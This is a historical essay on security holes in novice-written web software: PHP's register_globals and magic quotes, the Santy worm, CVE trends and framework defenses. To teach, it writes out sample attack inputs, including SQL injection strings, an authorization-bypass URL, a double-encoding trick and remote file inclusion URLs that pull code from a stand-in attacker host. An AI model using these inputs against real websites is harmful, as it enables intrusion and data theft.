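# Past waves of novice programmers and the vulnerabilities they brought

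## Who the new programmers were and how their mistakes became security holes

A novice programmer is someone without training or experience in professional development who writes software that others rely on. Several times since the mid-1990s, a new tool has brought in large numbers of them within a few years: first scripts for websites, then macros in office documents, then kits for building phone apps, and now AI systems that write a whole application from a plain-language description. Much of what they made was useful, but some of it also contained vulnerabilities, which are mistakes in software or its settings that let an attacker do something the owner did not intend.

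### What each tool took out of the work

A web page in 1994 was normally fixed text. To make one that remembered what visitors typed, its owner had to write a separate program, usually in C or Perl, that unpacked the browser's request, handled the files or database and printed a new page. Rasmus Lerdorf, who wanted to know who was reading his online résumé, wrote programs of this kind for himself. He also needed a way to "glue my home page to a database", as he put it in a magazine piece quoted in Cybercultural's *1995*. According to the PHP project's history, he released the source code in June 1995. His announcement, reprinted in PHP.Watch's *php turns 25*, offered a guestbook "in about 2 minutes" to people who had no access to Perl. They did need permission to run programs on the server, and Lerdorf added: "Ask your system administrator if you are not sure what this means." With PHP, as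 the tools came to be known, the owner of a page no longer had to write a separate program and could put a database query in the middle of the page and see the result at once.

Macros are small programs stored inside a document. Microsoft Office had them before 1995, when a macro virus, Concept, first spread widely among Word users. Office users could create macros without setting up a programming environment. For simple jobs they didn't even have to write code, since they could press "record", carry out the steps by hand and let Office produce it. Anyone who emailed a spreadsheet to a colleague also sent the macros inside it, which made it easy to distribute both useful programs and viruses.

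Phone apps followed in 2008, when Apple opened its App Store in July and Google opened its Android Market in October. The companies' development kits supplied ready-made buttons, maps and camera controls. The stores handled delivery and payment, so a student with a laptop could reach customers without first making a deal with a phone maker or network operator.

In February 2025 the AI researcher Andrej Karpathy named the latest wave "vibe coding". *Professional Software Developers Don't Vibe, They Control* (2025) quotes him as saying that developers who work this way "forget that the code even exists". The term has since broadened, and *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (Jha, Anand and colleagues, 2026) uses it both for professionals who direct AI agents from their editors and for people who cannot program and build applications by conversation on platforms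 such as Bolt and Replit. *Vibe Coding with Google AI Studio Case Study* (2026) describes one of these novices, a primary-school teacher who took an online course and then built an app for managing school trips, to solve a problem she and her colleagues had at work. Her specification, the AI's replies and the finished app are all in Romanian, so she did not even need English to build it.

All these tools made it easier to get a program to work, but making it safe took as much knowledge as before. The novice still had to know what an attacker might type into the form and who else could open the page.

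### How many people program without being programmers

The figure that researchers long repeated was 55 million Americans. It goes back to a 1995 prediction by the software engineer Barry Boehm for the year 2005, and it turned out to measure something else. Scaffidi, Shaw and Myers (2005), in *The "55M End-User Programmers" Estimate Revisited*, went back to Boehm's method and found that he had estimated the number of people who used computers in businesses, whether or not they programmed. They made new projections for 2012 from US labor statistics: 90 million computer users at work, over 55 million of them using spreadsheets or databases, over 13 million who would describe themselves as programmers, and fewer than 3 million professional programmers. (That 55 million turns up twice, with two meanings, is a coincidence that has probably confused many readers.)

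By these projections, self-described programmers outnumber professionals by more than four to one. The 55 million are only a pool of potential programmers, and most of them may never have written anything that a second person used. *End User Software Engineering* distinguishes professionals from end users by purpose. Professionals are paid to ship and maintain software, while end users write programs to support a goal in their own field. An accountant's private formula puts nobody else at risk, but it becomes a novice's program in the sense above when the rest of the office starts to depend on it.

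Newer counts seem at first to give a different picture. *Global Developer Population 2019 Community Edition* (2019), by the market researcher SlashData, put the world's developers at just under 19 million at the start of 2019, 13 million of them professionals. Bilic Arar's *There are 47 Million Developers in the World* reports that by early 2025 SlashData's estimate was over 47 million, including 36.5 million professionals, and that the number of amateurs had fallen by more than a million in a year. SlashData's *Global Developer Population* (2025) puts the total at 48.4 million in the third quarter of 2025. Professionals are thus a large majority in SlashData's counts, although they are a small minority in the American projections. The difference is probably due to whom each method can reach. SlashData uses surveys of developers, employment statistics and activity on sites such as GitHub,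 where programmers store and share code. The teacher with the school-trips app would probably not appear in any of these.

Surveys of the general public come closer to counting new programmers. Eurostat's *EU girls excel in digital skills, but trail in coding* (2026) found that 14.9% of internet users aged 16 to 19 in the EU had written code in the three months before its 2025 survey, though many of them presumably did so at school. In the United States, YouGov's *AI Usage* (2026) found that 11% of respondents had used AI to assist in coding, and another 25% said they would consider it. That 11% represents about 25 million adult citizens, including professional programmers, but the margin of error is nearly four points, so the true figure could be considerably lower or higher.

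The companies that sell the new tools publish the largest numbers. Lovable's *A first look at the build economy* (2026) reports that 80% of the people who build on its platform describe their roles as non-technical, and that their projects receive 720 million visits a month. The company also claims 50 million projects, according to Journal du Net's *Fabian Hedin (Lovable)* (2026). Stan's *Lovable* (2026) points out that nobody has audited the usage data. The project count also doesn't show how many people use the platform, since one user can start twenty projects and abandon them all. The visits matter more for security than the number of builders does, because they suggest that other people use a good part of this software.

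There is no direct count of novice programmers. Tens of millions worldwide is a reasonable guess, but a more exact figure would be hard to defend.

### A guestbook and its holes

Lerdorf's guestbook can illustrate most of the relevant vulnerabilities. Visitors enter a name and a message in a form, a database stores both, and the page shows the messages to every visitor. Suppose visitors can also mark a message as private, so that only the owner can read it, and the owner can log in and delete messages.

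Suppose too that there is a search box for finding messages by name. The easy way to program it is to paste whatever the visitor types into a query, which is a command to the database in a language called SQL:

`SELECT message FROM entries WHERE private = 0 AND name = 'Anna'`

The quotation marks show the database where the name begins and ends. A visitor who types `' OR '1'='1` instead of Anna closes the quotation early, and the remainder becomes part of the command:

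`SELECT message FROM entries WHERE private = 0 AND name = '' OR '1'='1'`

One always equals one, so the condition holds for every row and the database returns the private messages along with the rest. This is SQL injection, the best-known form of injection, an attack in which text from a user runs as a command. The apostrophe in an honest visitor's name, such as O'Brien, would trigger the same flaw and cause an error. Programmers can prevent this by sending the command and the visitor's text to the database separately, so the text can't alter the command.

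Cross-site scripting, or XSS, is the same confusion of text and command, except that the command runs in another visitor's browser. An attacker leaves a message containing a program between `<script>` tags. If the guestbook prints the message unchanged, the program runs in the browser of everyone who opens the page. When the owner opens the page, the program can do whatever the owner can do on the site. To prevent this, the guestbook must convert the special characters before it prints them, so that the browser displays the tag as text.

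In cross-site request forgery, or CSRF, the attacker uses the owner's browser to send a request to the guestbook. The owner logs in to delete some spam and, in another tab, opens a page that the attacker controls. A hidden form on that page sends the request "delete message 7" to the guestbook. Unless the site or the browser restricts it, the browser attaches the owner's login to the request, as it would after a real click, and the guestbook deletes the message. The usual defense is to put a secret random value, called a token, in each of the guestbook's own forms and reject any request without it.

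Access control, also called authorization, is the set of rules that decide which user may see or change which data. A beginner may try to protect a message only by hiding its "delete" link from everyone but the owner. The link is just an address, such as `/delete?id=7`, so if the program behind it does not check who is asking, anyone who types the address can delete the message. Such a request looks normal, with no stray quotation mark or script, which makes this hole harder to close with ready-made code than the other three. A general tool can convert every `<` on every page, but it cannot determine who may delete a message or read a private one unless somebody has stated the rule.

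The guestbook still works with all four holes in it. It saves and displays messages, and it passes the owner's tests. People who judge software by running it can therefore miss the holes. *From Prompting to Verification* (2026), a survey of 162 vibe coders ranging from non-coders to professionals, describes vibe coding as relying on this kind of check. It concludes that vibe coding widens access to making software without spreading equally "the expertise to evaluate it".

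### Levels of protection

Few people write a guestbook from scratch today. They build on a framework, which is ready-made code that can also apply protections for the developer. Frameworks vary in how much they leave to the developer, and Finifter and Wagner's *Exploring the Relationship Between Web Application Development Tools and Security* distinguishes four levels.

The strongest protection is *always on*, meaning the developer cannot remove it without giving up the framework. Their example is Spring Web Flow, a Java framework that uses tokens to track where each user is in a sequence of pages. The same tokens block CSRF, and developers cannot switch them off because the pages do not work without them.

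*Opt-out* protection is on unless the developer disables or bypasses it. One programming team in the study had a database layer that wrote the SQL itself and ruled out injection, but a developer in a hurry could still bypass it and send a handwritten query.

*Opt-in* protection covers the whole application after the developer turns it on once. Acegi Security, another Java package, offered several ways of storing passwords, and the developer had to select a secure one, which is a small task for someone who knows about it.

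*Manual* protection is a routine that the developer must call each time it is needed. Many frameworks have supplied manual XSS filters, which the developer must apply wherever a page prints a visitor's text. An attacker needs only one place where the filter is missing. If a guestbook prints such text in twenty places and its author remembers the filter 98% of the time, the chance of at least one omission is 1 − 0.98²⁰, or about one in three.

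Always-on and opt-out protections are safe defaults because they stay in place unless someone deliberately changes them. For novices, the important distinction is between opt-out and opt-in, because an opt-in protection helps only programmers who already know about the danger.

### Counting the harm

To find out whether a protection has helped, one has to count something, and there are three main candidates.

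Reported vulnerabilities are the easiest data to obtain. Since 1999, a public catalogue has listed known vulnerabilities in distributed software and given each a CVE (Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures) number. A hole in a guestbook script that thousands of people download can receive a CVE number, but the same hole in a guestbook written for one website normally does not, so the catalogue covers very little of what novices make for themselves. The number of entries also depends on how many people are looking for vulnerabilities.

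Vulnerabilities per thousand lines of code is a measure of the flaws in software, or at least those that a reviewer can find. Its weakness is that programs that do the same job can differ in length. In Finifter and Wagner's study, nine professional teams wrote the same web application, in versions ranging from 1,057 to 3,686 lines. Three flaws would come to 2.8 per thousand lines in the shortest version and 0.8 in the longest, although both provide the same service and give attackers the same number of ways in.

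Successful attacks are closest to what people care about, and the hardest to count. Many victims never notice, and others keep quiet.

The three can move in different directions. In this invented example, a community of guestbook authors adopts a better framework and automatic updates between year 1 and year 5:

| | Year 1 | Year 5 |
|---|---|---|
| Guestbook programs in circulation | 100 | 500 |
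| Total lines of code | 200,000 | 1,000,000 |
| Vulnerabilities present | 400 | 1,000 |
| Vulnerabilities per thousand lines | 2 | 1 |
| Share that researchers find and report | 10% | 30% |
| Reported vulnerabilities | 40 | 300 |
| Websites running the programs | 50,000 | 200,000 |
| Successful attacks | 5,000 | 2,000 |

Reports of guestbook vulnerabilities rise more than sevenfold, from 40 to 300. This is because five times as much code with half the density of flaws contains two and a half times as many flaws, and researchers find three times as large a share of them. Meanwhile, successful attacks fall by 60%, because automatic updates now close a reported hole on most sites before anyone exploits it. Some of the extra reports contribute to this fall, since developers can't fix a hole until someone finds it.

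Counting attacks in total can also give a different result from counting them per site. In the example, the rate falls from one site in ten to one in a hundred, so the total falls even though the number of sites quadruples. If the rate had only halved, to one in twenty, attackers would have broken into 10,000 sites in year 5, twice as many as at the start, even though each site was safer.

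## PHP and the settings that exposed beginners' websites

Around 2000, a PHP setting called register_globals let novices put a password on a web page without learning much. If the login form had a field named `password`, PHP put whatever the visitor typed there into a variable named `$password`, which the script could compare with the correct password. Kevin Yank, in an article for SitePoint, a website for web developers, counted this among PHP's biggest selling points. The setting was on by default, and according to the PHP manual, many people did not know it was a setting.

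### A login that anyone could skip

This is a shortened version of Yank's example:

```
if ($password == 'secret') {
    $authorized = true;
}
if ($authorized) {
    // show the private messages
}
```

A visitor who types the wrong password fails the first check, so `$authorized` never gets a value. PHP treats a variable without a value as false, so the messages stay hidden. The script works in every test its author is likely to try.

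With register_globals on, PHP made a variable out of every value that came with a request, from the end of the address as well as from form fields. If a visitor opens `guestbook.php?authorized=1`, PHP creates a variable named `$authorized` with the value 1 before it runs the first line of the script. The password test then fails but leaves `$authorized` at 1. PHP counts 1 as true, so the second test passes and the page shows the private messages. The attacker has to know the variable's name, but anyone can find it in a script available for download.

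Adding the line `$authorized = false;` at the top of the script fixes the vulnerability. Yank thought beginners should not have to write it, because visitors should have no way to change a script's internal variables. He expected half his readers to find the mistake stupid and many of the others to copy the script for their own use.

In July 2001 Shaun Clowes, a security researcher, complained on the mailing list Bugtraq that PHP encouraged insecure code by making it so easy to write. He also found the safe alternative, turning register_globals off, miserable to use, because a program then had to fetch each value from a list with a name like `$HTTP_POST_VARS` and declare that list again inside every function. Suraski (2001), in *[Security] PHP 4.1.0 available* credits this complaint with prompting a new design, which he and PHP's other developers released that December. Values from the address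 now arrived in `$_GET` and values from forms in `$_POST`, two short names that worked everywhere in a program. A script that needs the password reads `$_POST['password']`. If somebody adds `authorized=1` to the address, the value goes into `$_GET['authorized']`, which the script never reads.

Yank's rewritten script still doesn't set `$authorized` to false at the start, but visitors can no longer exploit this mistake once register_globals is off.

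PHP 4.2.0 turned `register_globals` off by default in April 2002. The PHP Group's *PHP 4.2.0 Release Announcement* presents this as the biggest change in the release, and the PHP manual calls it perhaps the most controversial change in PHP.

### Why people turned it back on

The new default reached fewer websites than one might think, because PHP reads its settings from a file on the server and an upgrade left that file unchanged. An upgraded server therefore got the protection only if someone turned register_globals off. The PHP Group's *PHP 4.1.0 Release Announcement* had assured users in advance that their existing settings would stay in place, and added that people with new machines could turn register_globals on if they chose. The developers felt they had little choice because, by their own account, the vast majority of PHP code relied on the feature.

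Companies with a lot of old code had a good reason to leave the setting on. In March 2002, a business user wrote to PHP's public bug tracker, worried that a future version would remove the setting for good (colins, 2002, *Observation on deprecation of register_globals*). He agreed with the security argument, but a huge amount of his company's code would break, and any part he missed in the repair would fail. He was happy with a default that protected novices as long as others could change it. One PHP developer replied that this meant changing one line in a file and asked what the problem was. Another wrote in June, after the new default had come out, that he hoped the setting would always be available, especially now that he had seen the impact of the change.

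Beginners had a different problem, which was that older tutorials stopped working. In a November 2002 report, *Can't get POST to work without register_globals = on*, judd (2002) described losing about two days to a tutorial whose examples seemed full of bugs. The tutorial dated from when register_globals was on by default, so on a newer server its forms appeared to send nothing. Judd complained that examples of secure code were "non-existent" and that newcomers had no idea what the security issues were. The reply apologized for the inconvenience and pointed to the release announcement. The report's title suggests that judd had already found the quick fix. A beginner in this position could get the tutorial working by turning the setting on, without studying a security problem that had not yet hurt anyone.

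Colin's compromise also relied on the person who changed the line being the one who bore the risk. Many novices rented space on a shared server, where the hosting company chose the settings for all its customers. If the company turned register_globals on to keep one customer's old online shop running, a beginner who had just signed up could get the setting too, without ever having heard of it.

Nobody seems to have counted the servers that kept `register_globals` on. OWASP's *PHP Top 5*, written around 2005 by the Open Web Application Security Project, a nonprofit that publishes security advice, treats leaving it on as a common mistake among hosting companies and advises developers to make their installation programs check for it. PHP's developers deprecated the setting in version 5.3.0, in 2009, and removed it in 5.4.0, in 2012, ten years after they had turned it off by default.

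### Backslashes for beginners

Another default was there to protect beginners from SQL injection. Its name was magic quotes. Whenever a value arrived from a visitor, PHP put a backslash in front of each quotation mark, which tells the MySQL database that the mark is part of the text. If a visitor to the guestbook from the first section searched for `' OR '1'='1`, the query became:

`SELECT message FROM entries WHERE private = 0 AND name = '\' OR \'1\'=\'1'`

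The database then looked for messages by someone with that peculiar name and found none. The guestbook's author had done nothing and was safe.

The protection failed for some queries. Suppose the guestbook finds a message by number, with `WHERE private = 0 AND id = 7`. Numbers need no quotation marks, so an attacker can send `7 OR 1=1`, which gives PHP nothing to mark with a backslash, and the database returns every message. Chris Shiflett, who wrote a book on PHP security, demonstrated a subtler way around the same kind of escaping. In some Asian character encodings, the code for a backslash can also be the second half of a longer character. If an attacker sends a suitable first half before a quotation mark, the database reads the added backslash as part of that character, and the quotation mark is no longer escaped.

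OWASP objected that magic quotes gave "a false sense of security". The setting was on for some servers and off for others, so programmers had to write code that worked either way. Those who didn't could add backslashes to text that already had them, which is why many websites of the period displayed names like O\\'Brien. OWASP itself had once recommended `addslashes`, a function that adds the same backslashes when a programmer calls it, but later described this as poor advice.

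No repair could have fixed the design of magic quotes, because PHP added the backslashes when text came in, before it was clear where the text would go. Text needs different treatment for a database, a web page and an email. PHP's developers deprecated magic quotes in 2009 and removed them in 2012, together with register_globals.

The better solution was to send the visitor's text separately from the command, which PHP's old MySQL functions, such as `mysql_query`, did not allow. They accepted only a finished command, so the programmer had to paste the text into it. From version 5.1, in 2005, PHP came with a library named PDO that offered prepared statements:

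```
$q = $db->prepare('SELECT message FROM entries
                   WHERE private = 0 AND name = ?');
$q->execute(array($name));
```

The question mark stands in for the name, which the program supplies in the last line. OWASP urged everyone to move to PDO quickly, but noted that most hosts avoided the safer versions of PHP because they feared that old programs would stop working. OWASP's sample code also wrongly put the placeholders inside quotation marks, where PDO does not recognize them, so a novice who copied it would have got an error and perhaps gone back to `mysql_query`.

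PHP's developers deprecated the old MySQL functions in 2013 and removed them from version 7.0 in December 2015. Code from the old tutorials stopped working in the new version, but programmers still didn't have to use prepared statements. The replacement library, mysqli, supports them but also accepts a command with a visitor's text pasted into it. Programmers using plain PHP must therefore still protect against SQL injection themselves, though many frameworks now do it for them.

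PHP's manual filter against cross-site scripting, the `htmlentities` function, also had an unsafe default. PentesterLab's *Is PHP REALLY Getting Better?* (2024) points out that until PHP 8.1, released in 2021, the function left single quotation marks unchanged unless the programmer told it to convert them. A programmer who called the filter everywhere it was needed could still leave a page vulnerable wherever it put a visitor's text between single quotes.

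### The Santy worm

In December 2004 a worm, a program that spreads from machine to machine by itself, showed how much damage one mistake in popular PHP software could do. Its target was phpBB, a free forum program that people could install without knowing how to program. When someone reached a discussion through phpBB's search, the address of the page contained the search words, and the forum highlighted them in the text. To do this it used an option of PHP's search-and-replace function that runs the replacement text as PHP code. (PentesterLab lists this option among the surprises that PHP 7.0 finally removed.)

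To add commands, an attacker needed to get a quotation mark into that code. Magic quotes should have put a backslash in front of it, but phpBB decoded the search words one time too many. In web addresses, `%27` stands for a single quotation mark and `%25` for a percent sign. The attacker sent `%2527`, which PHP decoded to `%27`. This contained no quotation mark, so PHP added no backslash. phpBB then decoded it again, which produced a bare quotation mark, and the server ran whatever came after it.

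The phpBB developers released a corrected version in November 2004. About a month later, the Santy worm began searching Google for phpBB forums. It broke into those that still ran an old version, replaced their pages with a notice that the site was defaced, and used each server to search for more. Estimates from the time put the number of infected sites at 30,000 to 40,000 within a day. The worm's spread slowed when Google blocked its searches.

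phpBB's developers were not beginners, but many of the people who ran forums with it were, and they had to notice the new version and install it by hand. The CVE catalogue has a single entry for the vulnerability that the Santy worm used, as it would for a vulnerability in a script with ten users.

### Running a stranger's code

PHP's `include` command loads another file and runs it as part of the current program. Beginners used it to keep a website's menu in one place. SANS, an organization that trains security specialists, gives an example of the dangerous form: `include($_GET['site']);`. A beginner who wrote this expected an address like `index.php?site=contact.php`, but PHP accepted a web address wherever it accepted a file name. If a visitor opened `index.php?site=http://evil.example/code.txt`, the server fetched the text from the attacker's machine and ran it, an attack called remote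 file inclusion. The attacker could then do anything the site's own programs could do, such as read the database password. OWASP's *Top 10 2007-Malicious File Execution* (2007) lists complete control of the system among the possible results. Other sites on a shared server were also at risk, because most hosts ran everyone's PHP programs under one account.

With register_globals on, a program could have this hole even if it never asked the visitor for a file name. In larger programs, a main file stored the path to the program's folder in a variable, say `$root_path`, and then loaded other files containing lines such as `include($root_path . '/header.php');`. An attacker could open one of those other files directly and add `?root_path=http://evil.example` to its address. Because the main file had not run, `$root_path` had no value, and register_globals set it to the attacker's. Few authors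 would think to check a value they had never requested.

Remote loading had been on by default since PHP 4.0.4. From version 4.3.4, only the hosting company could turn it off. OWASP explained that many companies left it on because turning it off would also have broken well-written programs that read news or prices from other sites. OWASP asked PHP's developers to change the default.

In November 2006, PHP 5.2.0 split the setting in two. A program could still read data from another site, but it could run code from there only if someone turned on a new setting, `allow_url_include`. Very few legitimate programs had ever needed to do that, so hardly anyone had a reason to reverse the change, unlike with register_globals. Attackers could still try to load files that were already on the server, and could run their own code by first hiding it in an uploaded picture or a log.

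### What MITRE found in 2006

The new default came at the end of 2006, the year remote file inclusion overtook buffer overflows in CVE, a catalogue of software vulnerabilities. *Vulnerability Type Distributions in CVE*, published in May 2007 by MITRE, which runs the catalogue, sorts 18,809 entries from 2001 to 2006 by type. Buffer overflows had long been the most common. They occur mainly in programs written in C and similar languages, when input that is too long spills into neighboring memory. Cross-site scripting and SQL injection had already overtaken them in 2005.

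| Entries in the CVE catalogue | 2001 | 2002 | 2003 | 2004 | 2005 | 2006 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Buffer overflow | 279 | 436 | 268 | 392 | 445 | 541 |
| Cross-site scripting | 31 | 187 | 89 | 278 | 728 | 1,282 |
| SQL injection | 6 | 38 | 36 | 142 | 588 | 944 |
| Remote file inclusion | 1 | 7 | 12 | 36 | 96 | 913 |
| All types | 1,432 | 2,138 | 1,190 | 2,546 | 4,559 | 6,944 |

MITRE describes the last jump in remote file inclusion as almost 1000%, but the rise from 96 to 913 is 851%. That increase amounts to a third of the whole catalogue's growth in 2006. Buffer overflows nearly doubled in number over the six years but lost their lead because the web flaws grew faster.

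MITRE put part of the blame on novices. Download sites offered many free web applications, many of them unfinished and written by "inexperienced programmers with easy-to-learn languages such as PHP". Operating-system vendors' advisories, which mostly cover professional software, contain only six cases of remote file inclusion among 4,893 entries. The low count supports MITRE's explanation less than it seems to, because operating systems include few PHP applications in which the flaw could occur.

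The people who looked for vulnerabilities were often also beginners. They could test a site for SQL injection by typing an apostrophe into a form, and for cross-site scripting by entering a short script tag. MITRE calls the amateur programs "fish-in-a-barrel" applications and thinks their large number was probably a major cause of the trend. Some had few users or none, so a flaw in them could add to the count without endangering anybody. Cross-site request forgery, by contrast, was undercounted. Consultants regularly found it in clients' websites, but automatic tools had trouble detecting it, and the catalogue has only five entries for 2006.

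So the figures cannot show whether, or by how much, novices' code was getting worse. But MITRE found solid evidence, in customers' posts on vendors' forums, that attackers regularly used remote file inclusion to break into web servers. It also linked the surge to criminals who were building networks of hijacked servers.

### Reports after the new default

MITRE's yearly counts end in 2006, and the later figures are patchy. CVE Details' *Security Vulnerabilities, CVEs, Published In 2007 (File inclusion)* lists 25 entries between November 27 and December 28, 2007, most of them in small PHP applications. MITRE's monthly average for 2006 was 76. One month is a small sample, and the two organizations may classify flaws differently, but a drop this large would be hard to explain by those factors alone.

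In the 25 entries, attackers could set variables with names such as `CONF[app_root]`, `php_root_path` and `ccms_library_path`. In more than half of the entries, the variable looks like one the program was supposed to set itself, which suggests that the attack depended on register_globals or on code that imitated it. Such attacks were apparently still realistic enough to report more than five years after the default had changed. According to the entry for p.mapper, a mapping program, one could argue that "the proper fix should be in PHP".

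CVE Find, a website that counts the catalogue's entries by type, listed 3,106 for file inclusion in 2026. Subtracting MITRE's 1,065 for 2001 to 2006 leaves about 2,000 for the following two decades, or 100 a year, compared with 913 in 2006. The same rough calculation gives about 670 a year for SQL injection, compared with 944 in 2006, and 1,700 for cross-site scripting, compared with 1,282. CVE Find may have put some old file inclusion cases under code injection, a separate category with 4,736 entries. Counting all of those as file inclusion would raise its average to only about 340 a year.

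Reports of file inclusion fell much further than reports of SQL injection, which is perhaps the best evidence that the default helped. Both flaws were common in the same kind of amateur PHP program, and the same people hunted for them, but PHP blocked remote inclusion unless someone enabled it and left programmers to prevent SQL injection themselves. OWASP's *Top 10 2010-Release Notes* (2010) also cites PHP's more secure default configuration as the reason for dropping malicious file execution, which had ranked third in 2007, from its list of the most serious web risks. OWASP had also switched that year from ranking flaws by frequency to ranking them by estimated risk, so the flaw's removal doesn't by itself show how much rarer it had become.

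Other changes may have contributed. In *Security Trend Analysis with CVE Topic Models*, Neuhaus and Zimmermann (2010) used software to group all 39,393 entries in the catalogue up to the end of 2009 by the words they had in common. They found that the share of PHP-specific flaws had been falling since 2007, especially those that let an attacker run code. They suggest that one reason was the end of support for PHP 4 in August 2007, which pushed website owners toward the safer PHP 5. That move would also have spread the new default, so the two explanations are hard to separate. Bug hunters may also have used up the easiest targets.

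Reports of SQL injection, meanwhile, kept growing. IBM's *X-Force 2008 Trend & Risk Report* records 134% more of them in 2008 than in 2007. IBM could not tell whether programmers were making more mistakes or researchers were doing more tests, but thought it was probably both. In the first half of 2008, it also observed criminals starting to use automated SQL injection to plant links in the databases of well-known websites, which sent visitors' browsers to malicious pages.

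IBM also found that 74% of the web application vulnerabilities reported in 2008 had no patch from the vendor at the end of the year. A hobbyist's abandoned program might never get a patch, but a safer PHP default could still protect it once the hosting company upgraded the server.

Attackers kept trying file inclusion after the number of reports fell. Imperva's *Remote and Local File Inclusion Vulnerabilities 101* (2012) ranks remote inclusion among the four most common attacks on web applications in 2011, five years after the new default. It also mentions a military dating site that the hacker group LulzSec had breached by remote or local inclusion. Imperva sold protection against such attacks, and the attacks in its figures did not necessarily succeed. Still, trying the same address on a million sites takes so little effort that even a small number of old servers could make the attempt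 worthwhile.

### Fourteen applications under a scanner

Counting flaws directly in the code gives a figure that doesn't depend on what interests bug hunters. For *Security of Open Source Web Applications*, Walden, Doyle and colleagues ran a commercial scanner on fourteen PHP applications chosen from the most popular on the download site Freshmeat, including phpBB, WordPress and MediaWiki, the software behind Wikipedia. The scanner checks code without running it and looks for dangerous patterns, such as a visitor's text being passed into a query. The researchers scanned one version of each application for every week from the summer of 2006 to the summer of 2008.

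The count at the start was 7,750 vulnerabilities in 872,319 lines of code, or 8.88 per thousand lines. At the end it was 4,628 in 1,404,178 lines, or 3.30 per thousand. The total fell even though there was far more code. SQL injection went from 31% of the vulnerabilities to 13%, or from about 2,400 cases to 600.

But vulnerability density rose in eight of the fourteen applications, despite two years of public discussion about PHP security. The large improvements came from WordPress, the webmail program SquirrelMail and a photo album named Photo Organizer, whose density fell from 121.4 vulnerabilities per thousand lines to 60.9. SquirrelMail's developers removed many flaws in a single week by rewriting how the program handled input.

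Walden and colleagues also checked whether each project's website offered advice on secure installation, an email address for reporting vulnerabilities, a list of known vulnerabilities, and guidelines for secure programming. Projects that offered more of these tended to improve more, with a rank correlation of 0.67 (1 would be perfect agreement). With only fourteen projects, this is suggestive at best, and it does not show that the web pages caused the improvement, since developers who care about security are likely to write guidelines and also to fix their code.

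In the two projects that the researchers checked by hand, 54 of the scanner's 298 warnings (18.1%) were false alarms. The flaws it could not detect turned out to matter more. *An Empirical Study of the Evolution of PHP Web Application Security*, by Doyle and Walden, examined the same applications again with a newer version of the scanner, which recognized 73 types of flaws instead of 13, and a different way of counting lines. Warnings per thousand lines were now 28.12 in 2006, 22.23 in 2007, 28.38 in 2008, 25.21 in 2009 and 19.96 in 2010. The large fall between 2006 and 2008 had disappeared, and an improvement appeared only in the two years after that. Photo Organizer, the main success of the first study, went from 202 in 2006 to 206 in 2010.

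The developers had probably made progress against some familiar flaws, particularly SQL injection, while others that the first scanner did not detect persisted or became more common. These were among the best-known PHP applications and had active communities behind them, whereas a guestbook that one person wrote for one website had nobody to scan it.

In Walden and colleagues' first study, dangerous file inclusion became more common over two years, and none of the fourteen projects reduced it substantially. Reports of it appear to have fallen over the same period. The two findings are compatible because a scanner checks the program, not the settings of the server that runs it. It treats an `include` line that accepts a visitor's text the same way whether or not PHP will load a file from another server.

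## Web frameworks that apply protections automatically

A safer PHP setting could block some attacks but could not correct the queries and pages that a novice wrote. A framework can correct many of these mistakes because it generates much of the query and the page itself. Two well-known frameworks, Ruby on Rails and Django (for Python), came out in the mid-2000s and gained more protections in the following years.

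### The guestbook with and without a framework

In plain PHP, the guestbook from the first section might print a visitor's message like this, with no defense against XSS:

`<p><?php echo $message; ?></p>`

The same line in a Django page is:

`<p>{{ message }}</p>`

Django converts the special characters in any variable that a template prints with double braces, so a `<script>` tag reaches the browser as the harmless text `&lt;script&gt;`. Developers have to write `{{ message|safe }}` to print a message unconverted, so those who forget about the protection still get it.

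This automatic escaping does not cover every case. Text inserted into JavaScript, for example, needs different treatment from text in a paragraph. Finifter and Wagner, whose four levels of protection appear in the first section, found no framework that handled the JavaScript case, and one of the teams they studied left three XSS holes by inserting text into JavaScript without the right escaping.

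For the search box, a PHP novice would paste the name into the query:

`$db->query("SELECT message FROM entries WHERE private = 0 AND name = '$name'");`

A Django developer writes no SQL at all:

`Entry.objects.filter(private=False, name=name)`

Django turns this into a parameterized query, like the prepared statements that PHP programmers could write with PDO. In Django, though, the safe version is also shorter, and a developer has to do extra work to send a handwritten query.

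The form for deleting a message shows how a framework stops CSRF:

```
<form method="post" action="/delete">
  <input type="hidden" name="id" value="7">
  <input type="hidden" name="token" value="k3Xv9qLw...">
  <button>Delete</button>
</form>
```

Django rejects any submitted form that lacks the right token. An attacker can copy the form to another website but can't fill in the token, because browsers don't let one website read another's pages.

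Django developers have to add a short tag to each form to include the token. If they forget, the form produces an error the first time they try it, so novices notice this mistake, unlike most security holes, in their own tests. But if they search for the error message, they will also find the line that turns the check off. The check applies only to the types of request meant for changing data, such as form submissions. If the guestbook deletes messages through an ordinary link like `/delete?id=7`, Django lets the request through without a token.

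### Nine teams build the same website

In 2007 a programming contest gave nine professional teams 30 hours to build People by Temperament, a site where members take a personality test and search for people they might like. Three teams used Java, three Perl and three PHP, and each chose its own frameworks. Finifter and Wagner later searched the nine programs for vulnerabilities. Finifter read all the code and confirmed each suspected vulnerability by writing an attack for it. They also ran a scanner that attacked the sites from outside. Finifter's review found 71 vulnerabilities and the scanner found 39. Both methods found 19 of the same ones, so the total was 91.

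| Language | Vulnerabilities in each team's program |
|---|---|
| Java | 4, 5, 8 |
| Perl | 4, 5, 33 |
| PHP | 10, 10, 12 |

A statistical test across all three languages found no significant difference (p = 0.592) because Perl's results varied too much. Most of that variation came from one Perl team that had no protection against XSS anywhere. When Finifter and Wagner compared the languages in pairs, PHP did significantly worse than Java (p = 0.033). The teams had chosen their own languages, so the Java programmers may have been better, although they averaged less experience (7.1 years, against 9.8 for the PHP programmers).

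Finifter and Wagner say in their slides that nine programs are too few to find such effects. They also cite a dataset from the testing company WhiteHat that covers more than 1,500 web applications. In that dataset, applications written in PHP and in JSP, a Java technology, averaged nearly the same number of serious vulnerabilities over their lifetimes, at 26.6 and 25.8 respectively. Perl applications averaged 44.8.

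The choice of framework seems to have mattered more. Only two teams had a framework with any support for preventing CSRF, and only their programs were safe from it. Two teams had no framework support for session management, which is how a site recognizes a logged-in user from one page to the next, and only those teams got it wrong. If frameworks made no difference, each of these perfect matches would have had a 1 in 36 chance, which the study reports as p = 0.028.

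One of the two teams that were safe from CSRF had only manual support, so that result alone doesn't show that automatic protection is better. The picture is clearer if one takes the study's results for CSRF, session management and password storage together and sorts them by level of protection. Nine teams and three flaws make 27 cases:

| Protection in the team's framework | Cases | Vulnerable |
|---|---|---|
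| Always on or opt-out | 6 | 0 |
| Opt-in | 7 | 4 |
| Manual | 1 | 0 |
| None | 13 | 12 |

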